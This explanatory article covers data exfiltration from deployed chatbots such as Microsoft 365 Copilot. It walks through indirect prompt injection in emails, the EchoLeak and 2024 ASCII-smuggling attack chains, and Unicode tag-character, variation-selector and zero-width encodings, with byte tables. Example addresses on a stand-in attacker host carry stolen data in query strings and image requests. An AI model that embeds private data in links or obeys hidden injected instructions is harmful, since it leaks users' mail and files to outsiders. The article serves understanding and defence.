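# Data exfiltration from deployed chatbots through hidden characters and output channels

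## How a chatbot's answer can send data to an outsider

Data exfiltration is the transfer of private data to someone not entitled to it, and deployed chatbots have opened a new route for it. An assistant such as Microsoft 365 Copilot, which works inside Outlook, Word and Teams, answers questions by searching a worker's mail and files, including emails from strangers. A stranger can write instructions into an email. If the assistant follows them, it may put private data into a link or an image address in its answer, and the data can then reach a server the stranger controls.

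The weakness is common. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) listed more than a dozen affected products going back to April 2023, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat. Vendors had promptly fixed almost all of these flaws, usually by blocking the route by which data left the product. It is much harder to change the language model so that a stranger's text can't steer its answer. Willison was still recording new cases in July 2026, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*.

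### One request, from question to screen

Suppose an office worker, Ana, asks Copilot what her company agreed with a printing firm. According to Microsoft, Copilot first searches Microsoft Graph, the service through which Microsoft's programs reach an organisation's emails, chats and documents, and adds what it finds to her question. Microsoft calls this step grounding. The language model then generates a response from the enlarged prompt. In its training material, Microsoft adds that Copilot runs security, compliance and privacy checks on the response before Ana sees it.

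Microsoft says grounding can draw on emails, files, chats and meetings, the public web, and anything the user attaches. For people with the paid Copilot licence, access to work data is on by default.

Everything the model takes into account for one answer is in its context window, a long stretch of text. Ana's might hold Microsoft's standing instructions, her question, a colleague's notes on the contract and three emails from outside the company, one of them possibly from somebody she has never met.

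Copilot retrieves only what Ana has permission to open. That rule keeps her from seeing her colleagues' private files, but it does little against the stranger, who may want Ana's own mail, which Copilot can search.

In the last step, many chat interfaces render the language model's text as Markdown, a simple notation for formatting. Words in square brackets followed by an address in round brackets become a clickable link, and an exclamation mark in front of the same pattern makes it an image. The browser then acts on these links and images without any information about who influenced the model's output.

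### Instructions inside the data

In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in an email, document or web page, and an assistant follows them when it reads the text. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the idea and demonstrated it on Bing Chat, then Microsoft's search chatbot. When a user opened the chatbot in a browser sidebar, text on the current web page could influence its behaviour, even text the user could not see. The paper also described delivering the instructions by email, and a cruder method in which the attacker persuades the victim to paste them into the chat.

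In an indirect injection, the user is the victim and has usually asked the chatbot for something ordinary, whereas in jailbreaking the user tries to persuade the chatbot to break its own rules.

Filtering out instructions is difficult because ordinary documents are full of them, and the wording alone doesn't show whether an instruction is a legitimate command. *The Devil is in the Context* (Chang, Nikolić and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a document with a line asking the reader to send the completed report to a certain address. That line is content to summarise if the user wants a summary, but a legitimate command if the user has asked the assistant to carry out the document's instructions.

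SQL injection is a comparable problem in older software, and it has a known fix. An attacker types a database command into a web form, and the database runs it. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the user's data separately so that the database can never run the data as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models have no equivalent. A model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the tokens so far, and has no separate input for commands. *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) describes the same arrangement in agents, where trusted and untrusted text end up in one token sequence and are processed by the same layers of the network.

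Developers use special markers to label which parts of that sequence come from the user and which from a web page or tool. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested how much these labels affect the model internally. They put different labels on identical passages and trained a probe, a simple classifier, to identify the label from the model's internal activity. Then they gave the model a conversation in which everything was labeled "user", including passages written in the style of the model's own reasoning. The style of those passages outweighed their label, and the probe rated them 85% likely to be the model's reasoning and 2% likely to be user text.

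Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% when the probe measured the least confusion to 70% when it measured the most. This is a correlation, but Ye and colleagues have causal evidence from a related attack that used imitation reasoning. When they rephrased the imitation in a different style but kept its argument, the success rate fell from 61% to 10%.

Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, go further and argue that perfect prevention is impossible within such a model. Part of their proof concerns the best possible guess at whether a piece of the model's internal representation came from a trusted or an untrusted source. If both are equally common, the smallest achievable error rate is

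½ × (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two sets of representations lie. It runs from 0, when they are identical, to 1, when they do not overlap at all. A distance of 0.98 leaves an error of 1%. Only complete separation brings the error to zero.

For single words the overlap is obvious, since "send" enters the network as the same list of numbers whether Ana or a stranger wrote it. Deeper in the network, context has changed each word's representation, and Pant and colleagues assume an overlap there rather than derive it. Their result also sets no minimum for the error, which could be tiny, and it doesn't cover systems in which a program outside the model decides what the assistant may do. So the theorem is an argument against guarantees that rely on the model alone, but it is compatible with models that resist nearly every attack.

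Newer models resist prompt injection far better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 of the company's browser scenarios. In a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, the success rate after 15 attempts was 2.0%, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) cites OpenAI's figures for GPT-5.6 Sol, which is still more vulnerable to attacks arriving through tools and outside content. These succeeded 3.77% of the time, compared with about 0.05% for attacks typed directly into the chat.

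Whether such numbers are low enough depends on how often an attacker can try. Email costs little to send, and an attacker can send the same message to every address in a company. In a Gray Swan competition that Dziemian (2026) summarised, 464 people made more than 272,000 attempts on 13 leading models, and every model failed at least once. Willison (2026) accepts that training has made injection much harder, but says even 6,000 failed attempts don't guarantee that someone with a better method would fail.

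### How an address carries data

An injected instruction does the attacker no good until something leaves the building. The commonest carrier is a web address. Here is a harmless invented one:

`https://stranger.example/page?note=blue-kettle`

The first part, `stranger.example`, names a server. No real site can have this name, because internet standards reserve the ending `.example` for illustrations. The next part names a page on that server, and everything after the question mark is extra information that the server can use in any way. Shops and search engines routinely use this feature, for instance to pass along a search term.

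Suppose "blue-kettle" is the code name of a product that Ana's company has not announced. When her browser opens the address, it sends the page name and the note to the server, and the server adds a line to its log:

`09:14 GET /page?note=blue-kettle`

The stranger reads the code name in the log. The page doesn't need to exist, since the server can record the request and then reply with an error. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes this kind of leak and points out that it can happen even if the chatbot's visible answer contains nothing sensitive.

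The stranger did not know the code name beforehand. The planted instructions only describe what to look for and where in the address to put it. The model has Ana's documents in its context window, so it finds the code name there and adds it to the address.

If this address is a link, it sends nothing until Ana clicks it. But a browser has to fetch an image to display it, and it does this as soon as the answer appears on the screen. If the model writes `https://stranger.example/dot.png?note=blue-kettle` as an image, the browser sends the request while Ana is still reading the first line. She may see a broken picture or notice nothing at all.

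An output channel is any feature of an answer or a tool call that can carry data outside, such as a link or an image. Microsoft (2025) gives other examples. An assistant that can write to a public code repository could publish the data there. Almost any tool could leak data one bit at a time if an outsider can observe whether the assistant used it.

Browsers have a partial defence against the image route, called a Content Security Policy (CSP). It is a list, sent with a web page, of the servers from which the browser may load images, fonts and other resources. Without one, the browser loads them from anywhere, as Medley and West explain in *Content security policy*.

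If the policy for Ana's chat page omits `stranger.example`, her browser will not request the picture, and the code name will not reach that server. This protection depends on which servers the policy allows, and it fails if one of them forwards requests elsewhere. A rule about images also does not cover an ordinary link that Ana clicks.

### What the attacker needs

Three conditions must all hold for an attacker to extract data, a combination Willison calls the lethal trifecta. The assistant must have access to private data, read untrusted content (text that an attacker can write or influence), and have a way to send that data outside.

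An ordinary office assistant can meet all three conditions even if nobody has made an obvious mistake. The product is meant to read Ana's mail, people outside the company send her mail, and answers are more useful with links and pictures. Removing any one condition stops the theft. An assistant that reads hostile email but can only display plain text, with no links, images or tools, might still give Ana a false answer, but it has no direct way to send her documents to anyone.

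EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, is the best-documented example of how little an attacker needs. The firm Aim Security disclosed it in June 2025, after Microsoft had fixed it. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, assume that the attacker has no password, no account in the victim's organisation and no way to query the victim's Copilot. The attacker's email contains text but no malware, so a conventional virus scanner has nothing to find. Greshake and colleagues had already observed that such attacks require little technical skill and almost no knowledge of the model.

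The attack works only if the email gets past the spam filter, the victim uses Copilot at least occasionally, and Copilot retrieves that email in answer to a question. To make retrieval more likely, Aim Security filled the message with passages on subjects that employees commonly ask about, such as taking leave, as Willison (2025) recounts in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'*. The instructions also had to get past Microsoft's injection detector, which the researchers managed by wording them carefully.

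"Little technical skill" describes the injection better than the whole attack, because EchoLeak also depended on gaps in Copilot's link filter and CSP that took expertise to find. An attacker could presumably take their time looking for such gaps in their own Copilot account.

David C prefers to compare this to the confused deputy, an old computer security term for a program that an attacker manipulates into using rights the attacker lacks. Copilot can open Ana's files, so the stranger, who cannot, only has to influence Copilot.

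### Where the click comes

Reports on these flaws usually classify them by what the victim has to do. A zero-click attack sends data out during ordinary use of the assistant, while a one-click attack does so only after the victim clicks a link in the answer.

EchoLeak used first a link and then an image. Reddy and Gujral describe a first version in which Copilot's answer contained a link with the private data in its address, so the data was sent only if the user clicked. Replacing the link with an image removed the need for a click, but Copilot's CSP blocked the request because the attacker's server was not on its list of allowed addresses. The researchers avoided the block by using a Microsoft Teams address, which was on the list and would fetch outside pages on request. The injected instructions and the stolen data could stay much the same across these versions, while the interface and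 the browser handled the address differently in each.

The term "zero-click" can mislead slightly, because Ana still has to ask Copilot something, and Copilot has to retrieve the hostile email while answering. But she does nothing that security training would warn her about. A one-click attack gives her a chance to hesitate before clicking, though she has less reason to suspect a link in an answer from her own company's assistant than one in a stranger's email.

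A crafted-link attack begins with the victim's click. Some assistants accept a question as part of a web address, so following the link opens the assistant with that question already entered. The attacker writes the question and sends Ana the link. Her click delivers the instructions as if she had typed them, so the attack doesn't depend on a search finding a hostile email in her mailbox. The data may then leave without any further action from her. This resembles persuading a victim to paste in a prompt, except that the link enters it automatically. Because the address belongs to the genuine assistant, the usual advice to check where a link leads does not help her much.

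### Hidden characters on the way in and on the way out

Invisible text can serve an attacker at two points. In the chatbot's input, it hides instructions from people who might otherwise notice them. Microsoft mentions white text on a white background and non-printing Unicode characters as ways to do this. Chang and colleagues describe a demonstration with tag characters, which are Unicode characters that mirror the ordinary Latin alphabet but normally do not show on a screen. The demonstration targeted a skill, a file of instructions that a user installs to equip Anthropic's Claude for some task. Someone reading the file would have seen sensible security advice, but Claude also received invisible instructions to run a command of the attacker's choosing.

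Hidden characters conceal the stolen data from the victim as it leaves the chatbot. Ana might stop before clicking a link that ends in a colleague's salary or a login code. If the model writes the same data in tag characters, the link can look normal while its address still contains all of the data. The 2024 Microsoft 365 Copilot case worked this way. This concealment matters most in one-click attacks, where the victim can inspect the link first, and less when an image loads automatically.

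An attacker can use either method alone, and often needs neither. Microsoft stresses that a plain text file with no special characters can carry an injection, and the EchoLeak email used ordinary business prose. A filter that strips invisible characters from incoming mail would not have changed that email. It would also miss hidden characters that the model generates in its answer.

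## How invisible Unicode characters carry text

Computers store text as numbers. Almost all current software follows the Unicode standard, which gives every character a number called a code point. Programmers write a code point as U+ followed by the number in hexadecimal, a base-16 system that uses the letters A to F for the digits ten to fifteen. For example, the letter g has the code point U+0067 (Butler, 2025, *Smuggling arbitrary data through an emoji*).

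In English text, one code point nearly always means one shape on the screen, but the Devanagari syllable की takes two code points, and some code points have no shape of their own. These invisible code points control where a line may break, whether two letters join, or which version of a character appears. A long string of them can sit between two visible words without taking up any room, so an ordinary-looking email can contain a second text.

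### A duplicate alphabet for labels

The best-known characters for hiding text were designed to label languages. *Language Tagging in Unicode Plain Text* (Whistler and Adams, 1999) proposed them so that internet protocols could mark which language a passage was in. Plain text has no formatting codes, so the label had to be part of the text, but programs also had to be able to tell it apart from the rest. The solution was a duplicate of ASCII, the old 128-character code for English letters, digits and punctuation. A program could spell out "fr" for French in the duplicate letters, and programs that didn't need the label could skip it.

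Unicode 3.1 added these tag characters in 2001, according to the reference page *U+E002E Tag Full Stop*. They occupy the block from U+E0000 to U+E007F. The Unicode Consortium's *Special Areas and Format Characters*, a chapter of the current standard, lists 97 of them. Of these, 95 duplicate the printable ASCII characters, including the space, and the other two are a character that ends a tag and one that introduces a language label.

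The Unicode Consortium writes that tag characters "can express only tag values and never textual content itself". This is a convention for software to follow, but the encoding doesn't enforce it, so tag characters can be used to spell out a sentence.

Hardly anyone used the labels, because markup such as XML worked better. The consortium deprecated the characters in version 5.1, discouraging their use but leaving them in the standard. Whistler, Adams and colleagues (2010), in *Deprecating Unicode Language Tag Characters*, then retired the original proposal, calling it "an idea whose time never quite came". They expected any effect of the change on internet security to be good.

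The consortium later lifted the deprecation from 95 of the characters in version 8.0 and from the end-of-tag character in version 9.0, so that they could be used to spell out flags. Only the character that announces a language label and the practice of labelling languages this way are still deprecated. Some recent papers get this history slightly wrong. *Reverse CAPTCHA* (Graves, 2026) dates the deprecation to version 5.0, and *On Seeding Watermarks to Detect Verbatim LLM Copy-Paste Responses* (Aiersilan, Yousefi and Pless, 2026) calls the whole block deprecated.

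England, Scotland and Wales originally had no flag emoji because the relevant international list of country codes treats the United Kingdom as one entity, according to Emojipedia's *Emoji Flags Approved For England, Scotland, Wales*. Each flag emoji now consists of a black flag, U+1F3F4, followed by a code in tag characters (`gbeng`, `gbsct` or `gbwls`) and the end-of-tag character. Software that supports the sequence displays all seven code points as one flag.

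These flags are almost the only reason tag characters appear in normal email. When Microsoft first searched email for characters from this block, the legitimate messages that kept triggering its detector all contained one of the three flags.

### "Hello" in tag characters

The duplicates stand in the same order as the originals, so hiding a character takes one addition:

hidden code point = 0xE0000 + ASCII code

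The prefix 0x marks a hexadecimal number. The ASCII code of h is 0x68, so the hidden h is U+E0068. The table below shows the conversion for the whole word, and its last column lists the bytes a computer stores for each hidden letter.

| Letter | ASCII code | Hidden code point | Stored bytes |
|---|---|---|---|
| h | 68 | U+E0068 | F3 A0 81 A8 |
| e | 65 | U+E0065 | F3 A0 81 A5 |
| l | 6C | U+E006C | F3 A0 81 AC |
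| l | 6C | U+E006C | F3 A0 81 AC |
| o | 6F | U+E006F | F3 A0 81 AF |

Subtracting 0xE0000 from each code point recovers the word. A 2016 Unicode Consortium document specifies the same subtraction for identifying the flag that a tag sequence represents. The scheme uses no key, so it hides text from people but not from a program that looks for it.

Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* (2024) includes a demonstration file that appears in a suitable browser as an empty pair of square brackets. A short script that prints the name of every code point reveals twelve more characters inside the brackets, which spell "Language Log".

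UTF-8, the usual method of storing code points as bytes, uses one byte for an ASCII character and four for a tag character, so "hello" grows from 5 bytes to 20 when written in tag characters.

Hidden text grows further in a web address, because addresses allow only a limited set of characters. Browsers write any other byte as a percent sign and two hexadecimal digits, a method called percent-encoding. The hidden h becomes `%F3%A0%81%A8`, which is 12 characters, and the hidden "hello" takes 60.

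At that rate, the code name "blue-kettle" from Ana's files needs 132 characters, and a six-digit login code needs 72. An address of 8,000 characters has room for at most 666 hidden characters. This is plenty for a password or a sales figure, but an attacker who wanted to extract a long email would have to shorten it or spread it over several addresses.

Percent-encoding also makes the data visible again, though usually where the victim won't look. The attacker finds the percent-encoded text in the server's log and decodes it into tag characters, then into ordinary letters.

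### Variation selectors and invisible binary

Tag characters can encode only ASCII text. Butler's scheme can also encode non-ASCII text because it uses variation selectors, which normally follow another character and choose between versions of it. For instance, a selector can switch a symbol to its emoji style or pick one form of a Chinese character. Unless the combination is on one of three official lists, the selector changes nothing on the screen, but software is supposed to keep it when someone copies the text, in case a later version of Unicode gives the combination a meaning.

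There are 16 selectors from U+FE00 to U+FE0F and another 240 from U+E0100 to U+E01EF. That makes 256, exactly the number of values a byte can have. Butler assigns the byte values 0 to 15 to the first range and 16 to 255 to the second:

- for a byte value below 16, hidden code point = 0xFE00 + value
- for any other byte value, hidden code point = 0xE0100 + (value − 16)

The letter h has the value 104. Subtracting 16 leaves 88, which is 58 in hexadecimal, so the hidden h is U+E0158. The word "hello" becomes U+E0158, U+E0155, U+E015C, U+E015C and U+E015F. Butler attached these five selectors to a smiling emoji, which looked the same as before.

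For English text, this takes four bytes per letter, the same as tag characters. The advantage is that bytes can represent anything a computer stores, including Chinese text, a picture or an encrypted file.

A third method uses only two invisible characters, one for binary 0 and one for 1. Graves uses the zero-width space (U+200B) and the zero-width non-joiner (U+200C). The letter h is 01101000 in binary, so it takes eight invisible characters, each three bytes long in UTF-8. A hidden "hello" therefore takes 40 invisible characters, which amount to 120 bytes, or 360 characters in a web address. In Graves's experiments, a 12-character instruction became 96 invisible characters.

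Both zero-width characters have everyday uses. The zero-width space marks where a line may break in languages such as Thai and Khmer, which put no visible spaces between words. The non-joiner stops neighbouring letters from connecting in Persian.

| Scheme | One hidden character carries | "Hello" in UTF-8 | "Hello" in a web address | What appears on the screen | Legitimate uses |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
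| Tag characters | One ASCII character | 20 bytes | 60 characters | Normally nothing; a flag if the sequence is valid | Flags of England, Scotland and Wales |
| Variation selectors | One byte of any data | 20 bytes | 60 characters | Nothing, unless the character before has a listed variant | Emoji styles, Chinese character variants, Mongolian letters |
| Zero-width binary | One binary digit | 120 bytes | 360 characters | Usually nothing; may affect line breaks, spacing or joined letters | Line breaks in Thai and Khmer, letter joining in Persian |

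The binary method is inefficient, but it works with almost any pair of invisible characters. In Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* (2025), the security researcher Johann Rehberger uses "invisible times" (U+2062) and "invisible plus" (U+2064) and lets the user choose a different pair. *Data Provenance Auditing of Fine-Tuned Large Language Models with a Text-Preserving Technique* (Li, Eichler and colleagues, 2025) assembles an alphabet of 121 invisible characters for marking documents. A filter that removes only the tag block would therefore miss many characters that can carry hidden text.

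Both alternatives came about a year after the first demonstrations with tag characters. A remark on the forum Hacker News about storing unlimited data in a single emoji prompted Butler's post, dated 8 February 2025. Rehberger built the binary version a few weeks later, after the post had circulated on the forum. Graves reports that Gao and colleagues then used variation selectors in 2025 for jailbreaks that change how a model splits up a request without changing how the request looks.

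### Why a model can read what the screen leaves out

Displaying text and passing it to a language model are separate processes. To display a character, software looks for a matching shape in a font. It normally finds none for a tag character and, as Unicode recommends, leaves no gap or empty box.

A program called a tokenizer divides the original string of code points, not the displayed text, into tokens and gives the model a number for each one. *Out of Sight* (2026) points out that the common types of tokenizer produce numbers for invisible characters too. Some tokenizers have no token for a rare character but can still represent it as separate bytes.

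Invisible characters can become visible when software misreads their encoding. Several people who opened Language Log's file saw rows of accented letters and symbols because their browsers decoded it with an older Windows encoding instead of UTF-8. Mark Liberman, who posted the file, thought it would be safer if browsers always displayed tag characters as gibberish. The Unicode Consortium allows software to offer a mode that reveals hidden characters, but developers of ordinary chat windows have little reason to turn one on.

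A token number alone doesn't link U+E0068 to the letter h. In Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool* (2024), Rehberger attributes models' ability to read tag characters to the presence of those characters in the training data. This is plausible, since the invisible characters that Li and colleagues used to mark documents survived six standard data-cleaning procedures, including those used for C4 and the Pile. Ten tokenizers, including GPT-4o's, also recognised the characters reliably.

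They then further trained two small open models, LLaMA-2-7B and Mistral-7B, on documents with invisible marks. Each mark had two parts, and they tested whether a model given the first part would write the second. The models did so often enough for the researchers to detect 96.7% of the marked collections with no false alarms. So a model can learn to produce invisible text. But these marks had no meaning, and repeating a memorised sequence is easier than recognising that another sequence spells "hello".

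The arrangement of the bytes probably helps with the harder task. In the table for "hello", the letters share their first three bytes and differ only in the last. The last bytes follow alphabetical order, from A1 for a to BA for z. A model that processes separate bytes would only have to learn one shifted alphabet, which is a very simple cipher. This is an inference from the encoding, and it may not apply to a tokenizer that divides the characters differently.

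Each hidden letter is a single code point. The hidden h is encoded as F3 A0 81 A8, which doesn't include 68, the byte for an ordinary h. So the competing account in Cisco's *Understanding and mitigating Unicode tag prompt injection*, which credits it to Rich Harang, can't be quite right. In that account, a hidden letter consists of a tag followed by the original letter, and the tokenizer separates the two. The tokenizer preserves enough information to identify the letter, but the model still has to map it to the ordinary one.

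An attacker can also explain the encoding to the model, or rely on the model to run a program that decodes it. Butler found that models seemed not to attempt decoding variation selectors by themselves. With a tool for running code, some succeeded, and Google's Gemini 2 Flash solved one example in seven seconds. Rehberger gave ChatGPT a written description of the binary scheme and asked it to encode a sentence. This worked when ChatGPT could run code and gave mixed results when it couldn't. These tests used models from early 2025, and Rehberger expected stronger models to handle such encodings more reliably.

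If a stranger has to explain the code in readable words, Ana might notice the explanation even though she can't see the message. Tag characters are more useful to an attacker because many models read them without an explanation. In 2025, Embrace The Red's *Google Jules is Vulnerable To Invisible Prompt Injection* reported that the latest Gemini models did so "quite reliably".

Only experiments can show how often a model will obey hidden text, because this can't be worked out from the encodings alone. In a harmless use of the technique, Aiersilan and colleagues built a tool that lets teachers add an invisible instruction to an assignment, so that a chatbot's answer will contain a telltale line if a student pastes in the whole text. This works only if the tag characters reach the model and the model acts on them, and some of the chatbots they tried never produced the line. Graves's results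 vary widely with the model, the encoding and the tools available.

### The discovery of the attack

Researchers knew before 2024 that invisible characters could interfere with language software. Aiersilan and colleagues cite a 2022 survey by Boucher and colleagues that covered these characters, lookalike letters and hidden deletions. A chatbot's ability to read a whole message in tag characters and follow it came as a surprise.

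Riley Goodside demonstrated this on Twitter on 11 January 2024. Robust Intelligence's *AI cyber threat intelligence roundup January 2024* (2024) gives that date. Twitter builds post IDs from the time of posting, and the ID in Cisco's link to the post corresponds to 18:24 UTC on the same day.

According to the security firm Protect AI, the demonstration combined an ordinary question about some pasted text, a harmless-looking passage, and an invisible ending in tag characters. The ending was an instruction to ChatGPT to create a picture with the image generator DALL-E, and ChatGPT did so.

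Someone else may have found the trick earlier. On 12 January the pseudonymous programmer ShadowOpz (2024) published a script for producing such text. In the accompanying notes, ShadowOpz dates the first version to September 2023, says it was too valuable to attackers to release, and credits Goodside and another Twitter user, rezo_, with the public discovery. The notes are the only evidence for the earlier date.

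Rehberger's post about the ASCII Smuggler followed on 14 January, according to Language Log. The tool converts ordinary text to tag characters and back, so people can test their own systems or check a suspicious passage. The technique's usual name, ASCII smuggling, comes from this post.

Rehberger noted in his 2024 slides, *HackSpaceCon New Important Instructions* (Embrace The Red), that OpenAI had fixed the problem Goodside found, but Anthropic did not then consider this kind of hidden text a security risk.

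Rehberger had shown in January that ChatGPT could also write hidden text. A customised version took whatever the user typed and repeated it in tag characters between the words START and END. The user saw only those two words, but pasting the answer into the ASCII Smuggler revealed the text. Someone who copied an answer like this into an email would send the hidden text too.

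## The 2024 Microsoft 365 Copilot case

Three days after publishing the ASCII Smuggler, Rehberger reported to Microsoft that 365 Copilot was vulnerable to ASCII smuggling. By March 2024 he could make Copilot find a private email and hide its text in a link, which sent the text to his server if the user clicked it. He published the details in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* that August, after the attack had stopped working.

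Aim Security found EchoLeak in January 2025, and Reddy and Gujral call it the first known case of a prompt injection extracting data from an AI system in commercial use. Rehberger had used prompt injection to extract data from the same product eleven months earlier, although his attack required the victim to do more.

### From a stranger's email to a stranger's server

The attack starts with an email that contains instructions for Copilot. In Rehberger's demonstration most of the text was readable, though he notes that an attacker could hide it, for instance with a white font. The attacker could also put the instructions in a document, then share it with the victim uninvited or hope that Copilot retrieves it while answering a question.

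Suppose Ana receives such an email and asks Copilot to summarize it. Copilot follows the instructions in the email and searches her mailbox for a second message that the stranger wants. Ana did not ask for this search, and Copilot does not check with her before running it. Rehberger calls this automatic tool invocation, where a tool is any function the model can call, such as a search of mail and files. He had expected the injection to succeed because nobody had a fix for it, but the search surprised him.

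The second email is now in the context window. Copilot converts the email's text to tag characters, adds them to the end of an address on the stranger's server, and shows Ana the link with a reminder to click it for details. She sees a short, ordinary address. If she clicks, her browser sends the whole address, including the hidden characters. The stranger copies it from the server's log into the ASCII Smuggler, which has a setting for decoding addresses, and reads the email.

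Copilot needed help encoding text accurately, so Rehberger's hostile email included an example link with a short greeting already hidden in it. Accuracy matters because a sign-in code with one wrong character is useless.

Rehberger also describes two variations. The hidden text can go into an email address instead of a web address, so a click opens a new message to the attacker. This worked in some email programs. The instructions can also depend on who is reading. Copilot knows its user's name, job title and manager, and in Embrace The Red's *Who Am I?* Rehberger recounts sending one email to three people, including himself. Copilot gave each of them a different response, as the email instructed. An attacker could use this to target only a chief executive.

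### Sales figures and sign-in codes

The first demonstration, in February, extracted sales figures. The second, in March, targeted codes for signing in to Slack, a workplace chat service. These codes arrive by email, so Copilot only had to find the message containing the code in the user's inbox.

Sales figures and sign-in codes are both short enough to hide in one web address, but a code would be harder to exploit. Sales figures can stay valuable for weeks, whereas a code normally expires soon after it arrives, so a thief would need the victim to open the email and click at about the right moment. Rehberger does not report signing in to anything with a stolen code.

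The attacker must also know what to look for. Rehberger's published instructions identify the target email by its date and subject line, which an outsider would rarely know. Slack codes are easier to find, since the messages presumably use similar wording for everyone.

### What each step added

Rehberger used a link because Microsoft had closed a better route. In 2023 he had shown that Bing Chat could leak private data through an image. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* recounts that Microsoft told him in June that year that it had fixed this, apparently with a CSP that allowed images from only a few of its own servers. He doesn't describe trying images on 365 Copilot in 2024, but its web page had such a policy by the time of EchoLeak. Ravia (2025) lists the allowed servers in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*.

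Without images, the attack worked only if Ana clicked the link, and the tag characters affected only whether she did. A click would have delivered the same email just as well if Copilot had written it in plain letters at the end of the link.

Other attacks on Copilot leaked data without hidden characters. Willison's *Links and materials for Living off Microsoft Copilot* describes one that Michael Bargury of the security firm Zenity demonstrated in August 2024. An email instructed Copilot to search the company's files for the answer to a yes-or-no question about earnings, then show one of two links depending on the answer. Neither address contained private data, but the attacker could tell from the victim's click which answer Copilot had found. The attack leaked only one bit of information, but that might be all someone trading shares needs.

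In Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, Rehberger describes a later attack that needed neither a click nor hidden characters. Copilot again searched the mailbox on a stranger's instructions, but this time the data went out in a request for a font. Microsoft fixed the vulnerability in March 2026.

It is unclear how much the concealment helped in 2024. Tag characters do not disguise the server's name, and Rehberger notes that hovering over his sample link shows something is wrong. Visible text might have worked nearly as well. In the Bing Chat attack he had used base64, a common way of writing data as a string of letters and digits, and many legitimate links end in similar strings. He did not test whether people would click one kind of link more often than the other.

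The automatic search was more important. Without it, the attacker could have reached only what was in the context window, meaning the hostile email, the conversation, and whatever Copilot had retrieved for Ana's question. The later EchoLeak attack worked within that limit by asking for the most sensitive item in the context. But the 2024 attacker could target anything in the mailbox, including a message unrelated to Ana's question.

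The link was the exfiltration channel. If Copilot had found the Slack code and only displayed it, only Ana would have seen it, and she was entitled to it anyway.

### Errors in the press coverage

Several news accounts got this chain wrong, usually by putting the hidden characters in the wrong place. The attack did not require Copilot to have access to other programs such as Slack, although TechRadar's *Microsoft Copilot could have been hacked by some very low-tech methods* lists that access as one of three requirements. The codes were in the user's email, and Rehberger's later summary of his research, *Trust No AI* (2024), refers only to information from the inbox.

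In Rehberger's demonstration, the important hidden text was the stolen email being sent out. TechRadar also reports that the attacker smuggled the prompt in invisible characters, and Redmondmag's *Posey's Tips & Tricks* (2024) explains ASCII smuggling as a way to get hidden text into a prompt. An attacker can do that, and Rehberger mentions it as an option.

The visible part of Copilot's answer enticed the user to click, and the ASCII smuggling removed a reason to hesitate. The Hacker News' *Microsoft Fixes ASCII Smuggling Flaw* says the smuggling itself enticed the user. The links contained only the text of an email, though SC Media's *‘ASCII Smuggling’ attack exposes sensitive Microsoft Copilot data* refers to malicious code hidden in them.

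Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks* describes the chain accurately. It ends with advice that companies should control who creates and publishes Copilots, which isn't in Rehberger's write-up. The Hacker News quotes him giving that advice about a separate problem, publicly exposed bots that customers had built with Copilot Studio.

The confusion over direction matters because stripping tag characters from incoming mail would have left the readable instructions intact. It would have deleted Rehberger's worked example, and perhaps made Copilot's encoding less accurate.

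### Seven months from report to publication

Rehberger's write-up includes a log of his dealings with the Microsoft Security Response Center, the team that handles reports of flaws.

| Date in 2024 | Event |
|---|---|
| 17 January | Rehberger reports that Copilot is vulnerable to ASCII smuggling |
| 18 January | Microsoft closes the report as low severity; Rehberger objects and gets no response |
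| 10 February | Rehberger submits a complete attack that extracts sales data |
| 13 February | Microsoft opens an internal case |
| 14 March | Rehberger shares the version that steals Slack codes |
| 9 April | Microsoft asks for time until the end of May |
| 16 May | Microsoft says it is still working on a comprehensive fix |
| 2 July | Rehberger asks about progress because his attack no longer works |
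| 31 July | Microsoft asks to review a draft of the write-up |
| 22 August | Microsoft raises no concerns about publication |
| 24 August | Rehberger presents the attack at the HITCON security conference |

The post itself followed on 26 August, according to SC Media.

The first rating had some basis, since hidden text leaks nothing by itself. Rehberger objected that the same behaviour would be more serious as part of an attack chain, and he built one within a month. Microsoft explained in 2025 that it treats a prompt injection as a vulnerability only when it has a security impact, such as data theft. By that standard, the February report described a vulnerability, while the January report described only one of its components. The weakness of this approach is that Microsoft does not act until someone outside the company assembles the components, which an attacker can do as well as a researcher.

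The theft of sales figures seems to have been enough to make Microsoft reconsider. Infosecurity Magazine credits the theft of sign-in codes, but according to the log, Microsoft had opened its internal case a month before Rehberger sent that version.

Rehberger had wanted to present the attack at HackSpaceCon in April but left it out at Microsoft's request. *New Important Instructions* (Rehberger, 2024), the slides for that talk, still shows how an attacker could append hidden data to a link or an email address, but not that this worked in Copilot. The general idea was therefore public for months while Copilot was still vulnerable. Rehberger withheld the demonstration that Copilot would search a mailbox and complete the whole attack chain.

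The date of the fix is uncertain. *Trust No AI* puts it in July, but 2 July is only the day Rehberger told Microsoft that the attack had failed. In August he wrote that links seemed to have stopped rendering "a few months ago", which would fit May or June better. Microsoft may also have made more than one change.

### Three recommendations and an unexplained fix

Rehberger's report to Microsoft recommended changes at three points in the chain:

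- Copilot should not interpret tag characters or display them in its answers.
- It should not run tools automatically while prompt injection has no fix, because an attacker can use them to bring private data into the conversation and probably to take actions as well.
- Ideally it should not render links at all, since they help with phishing as well as with theft.

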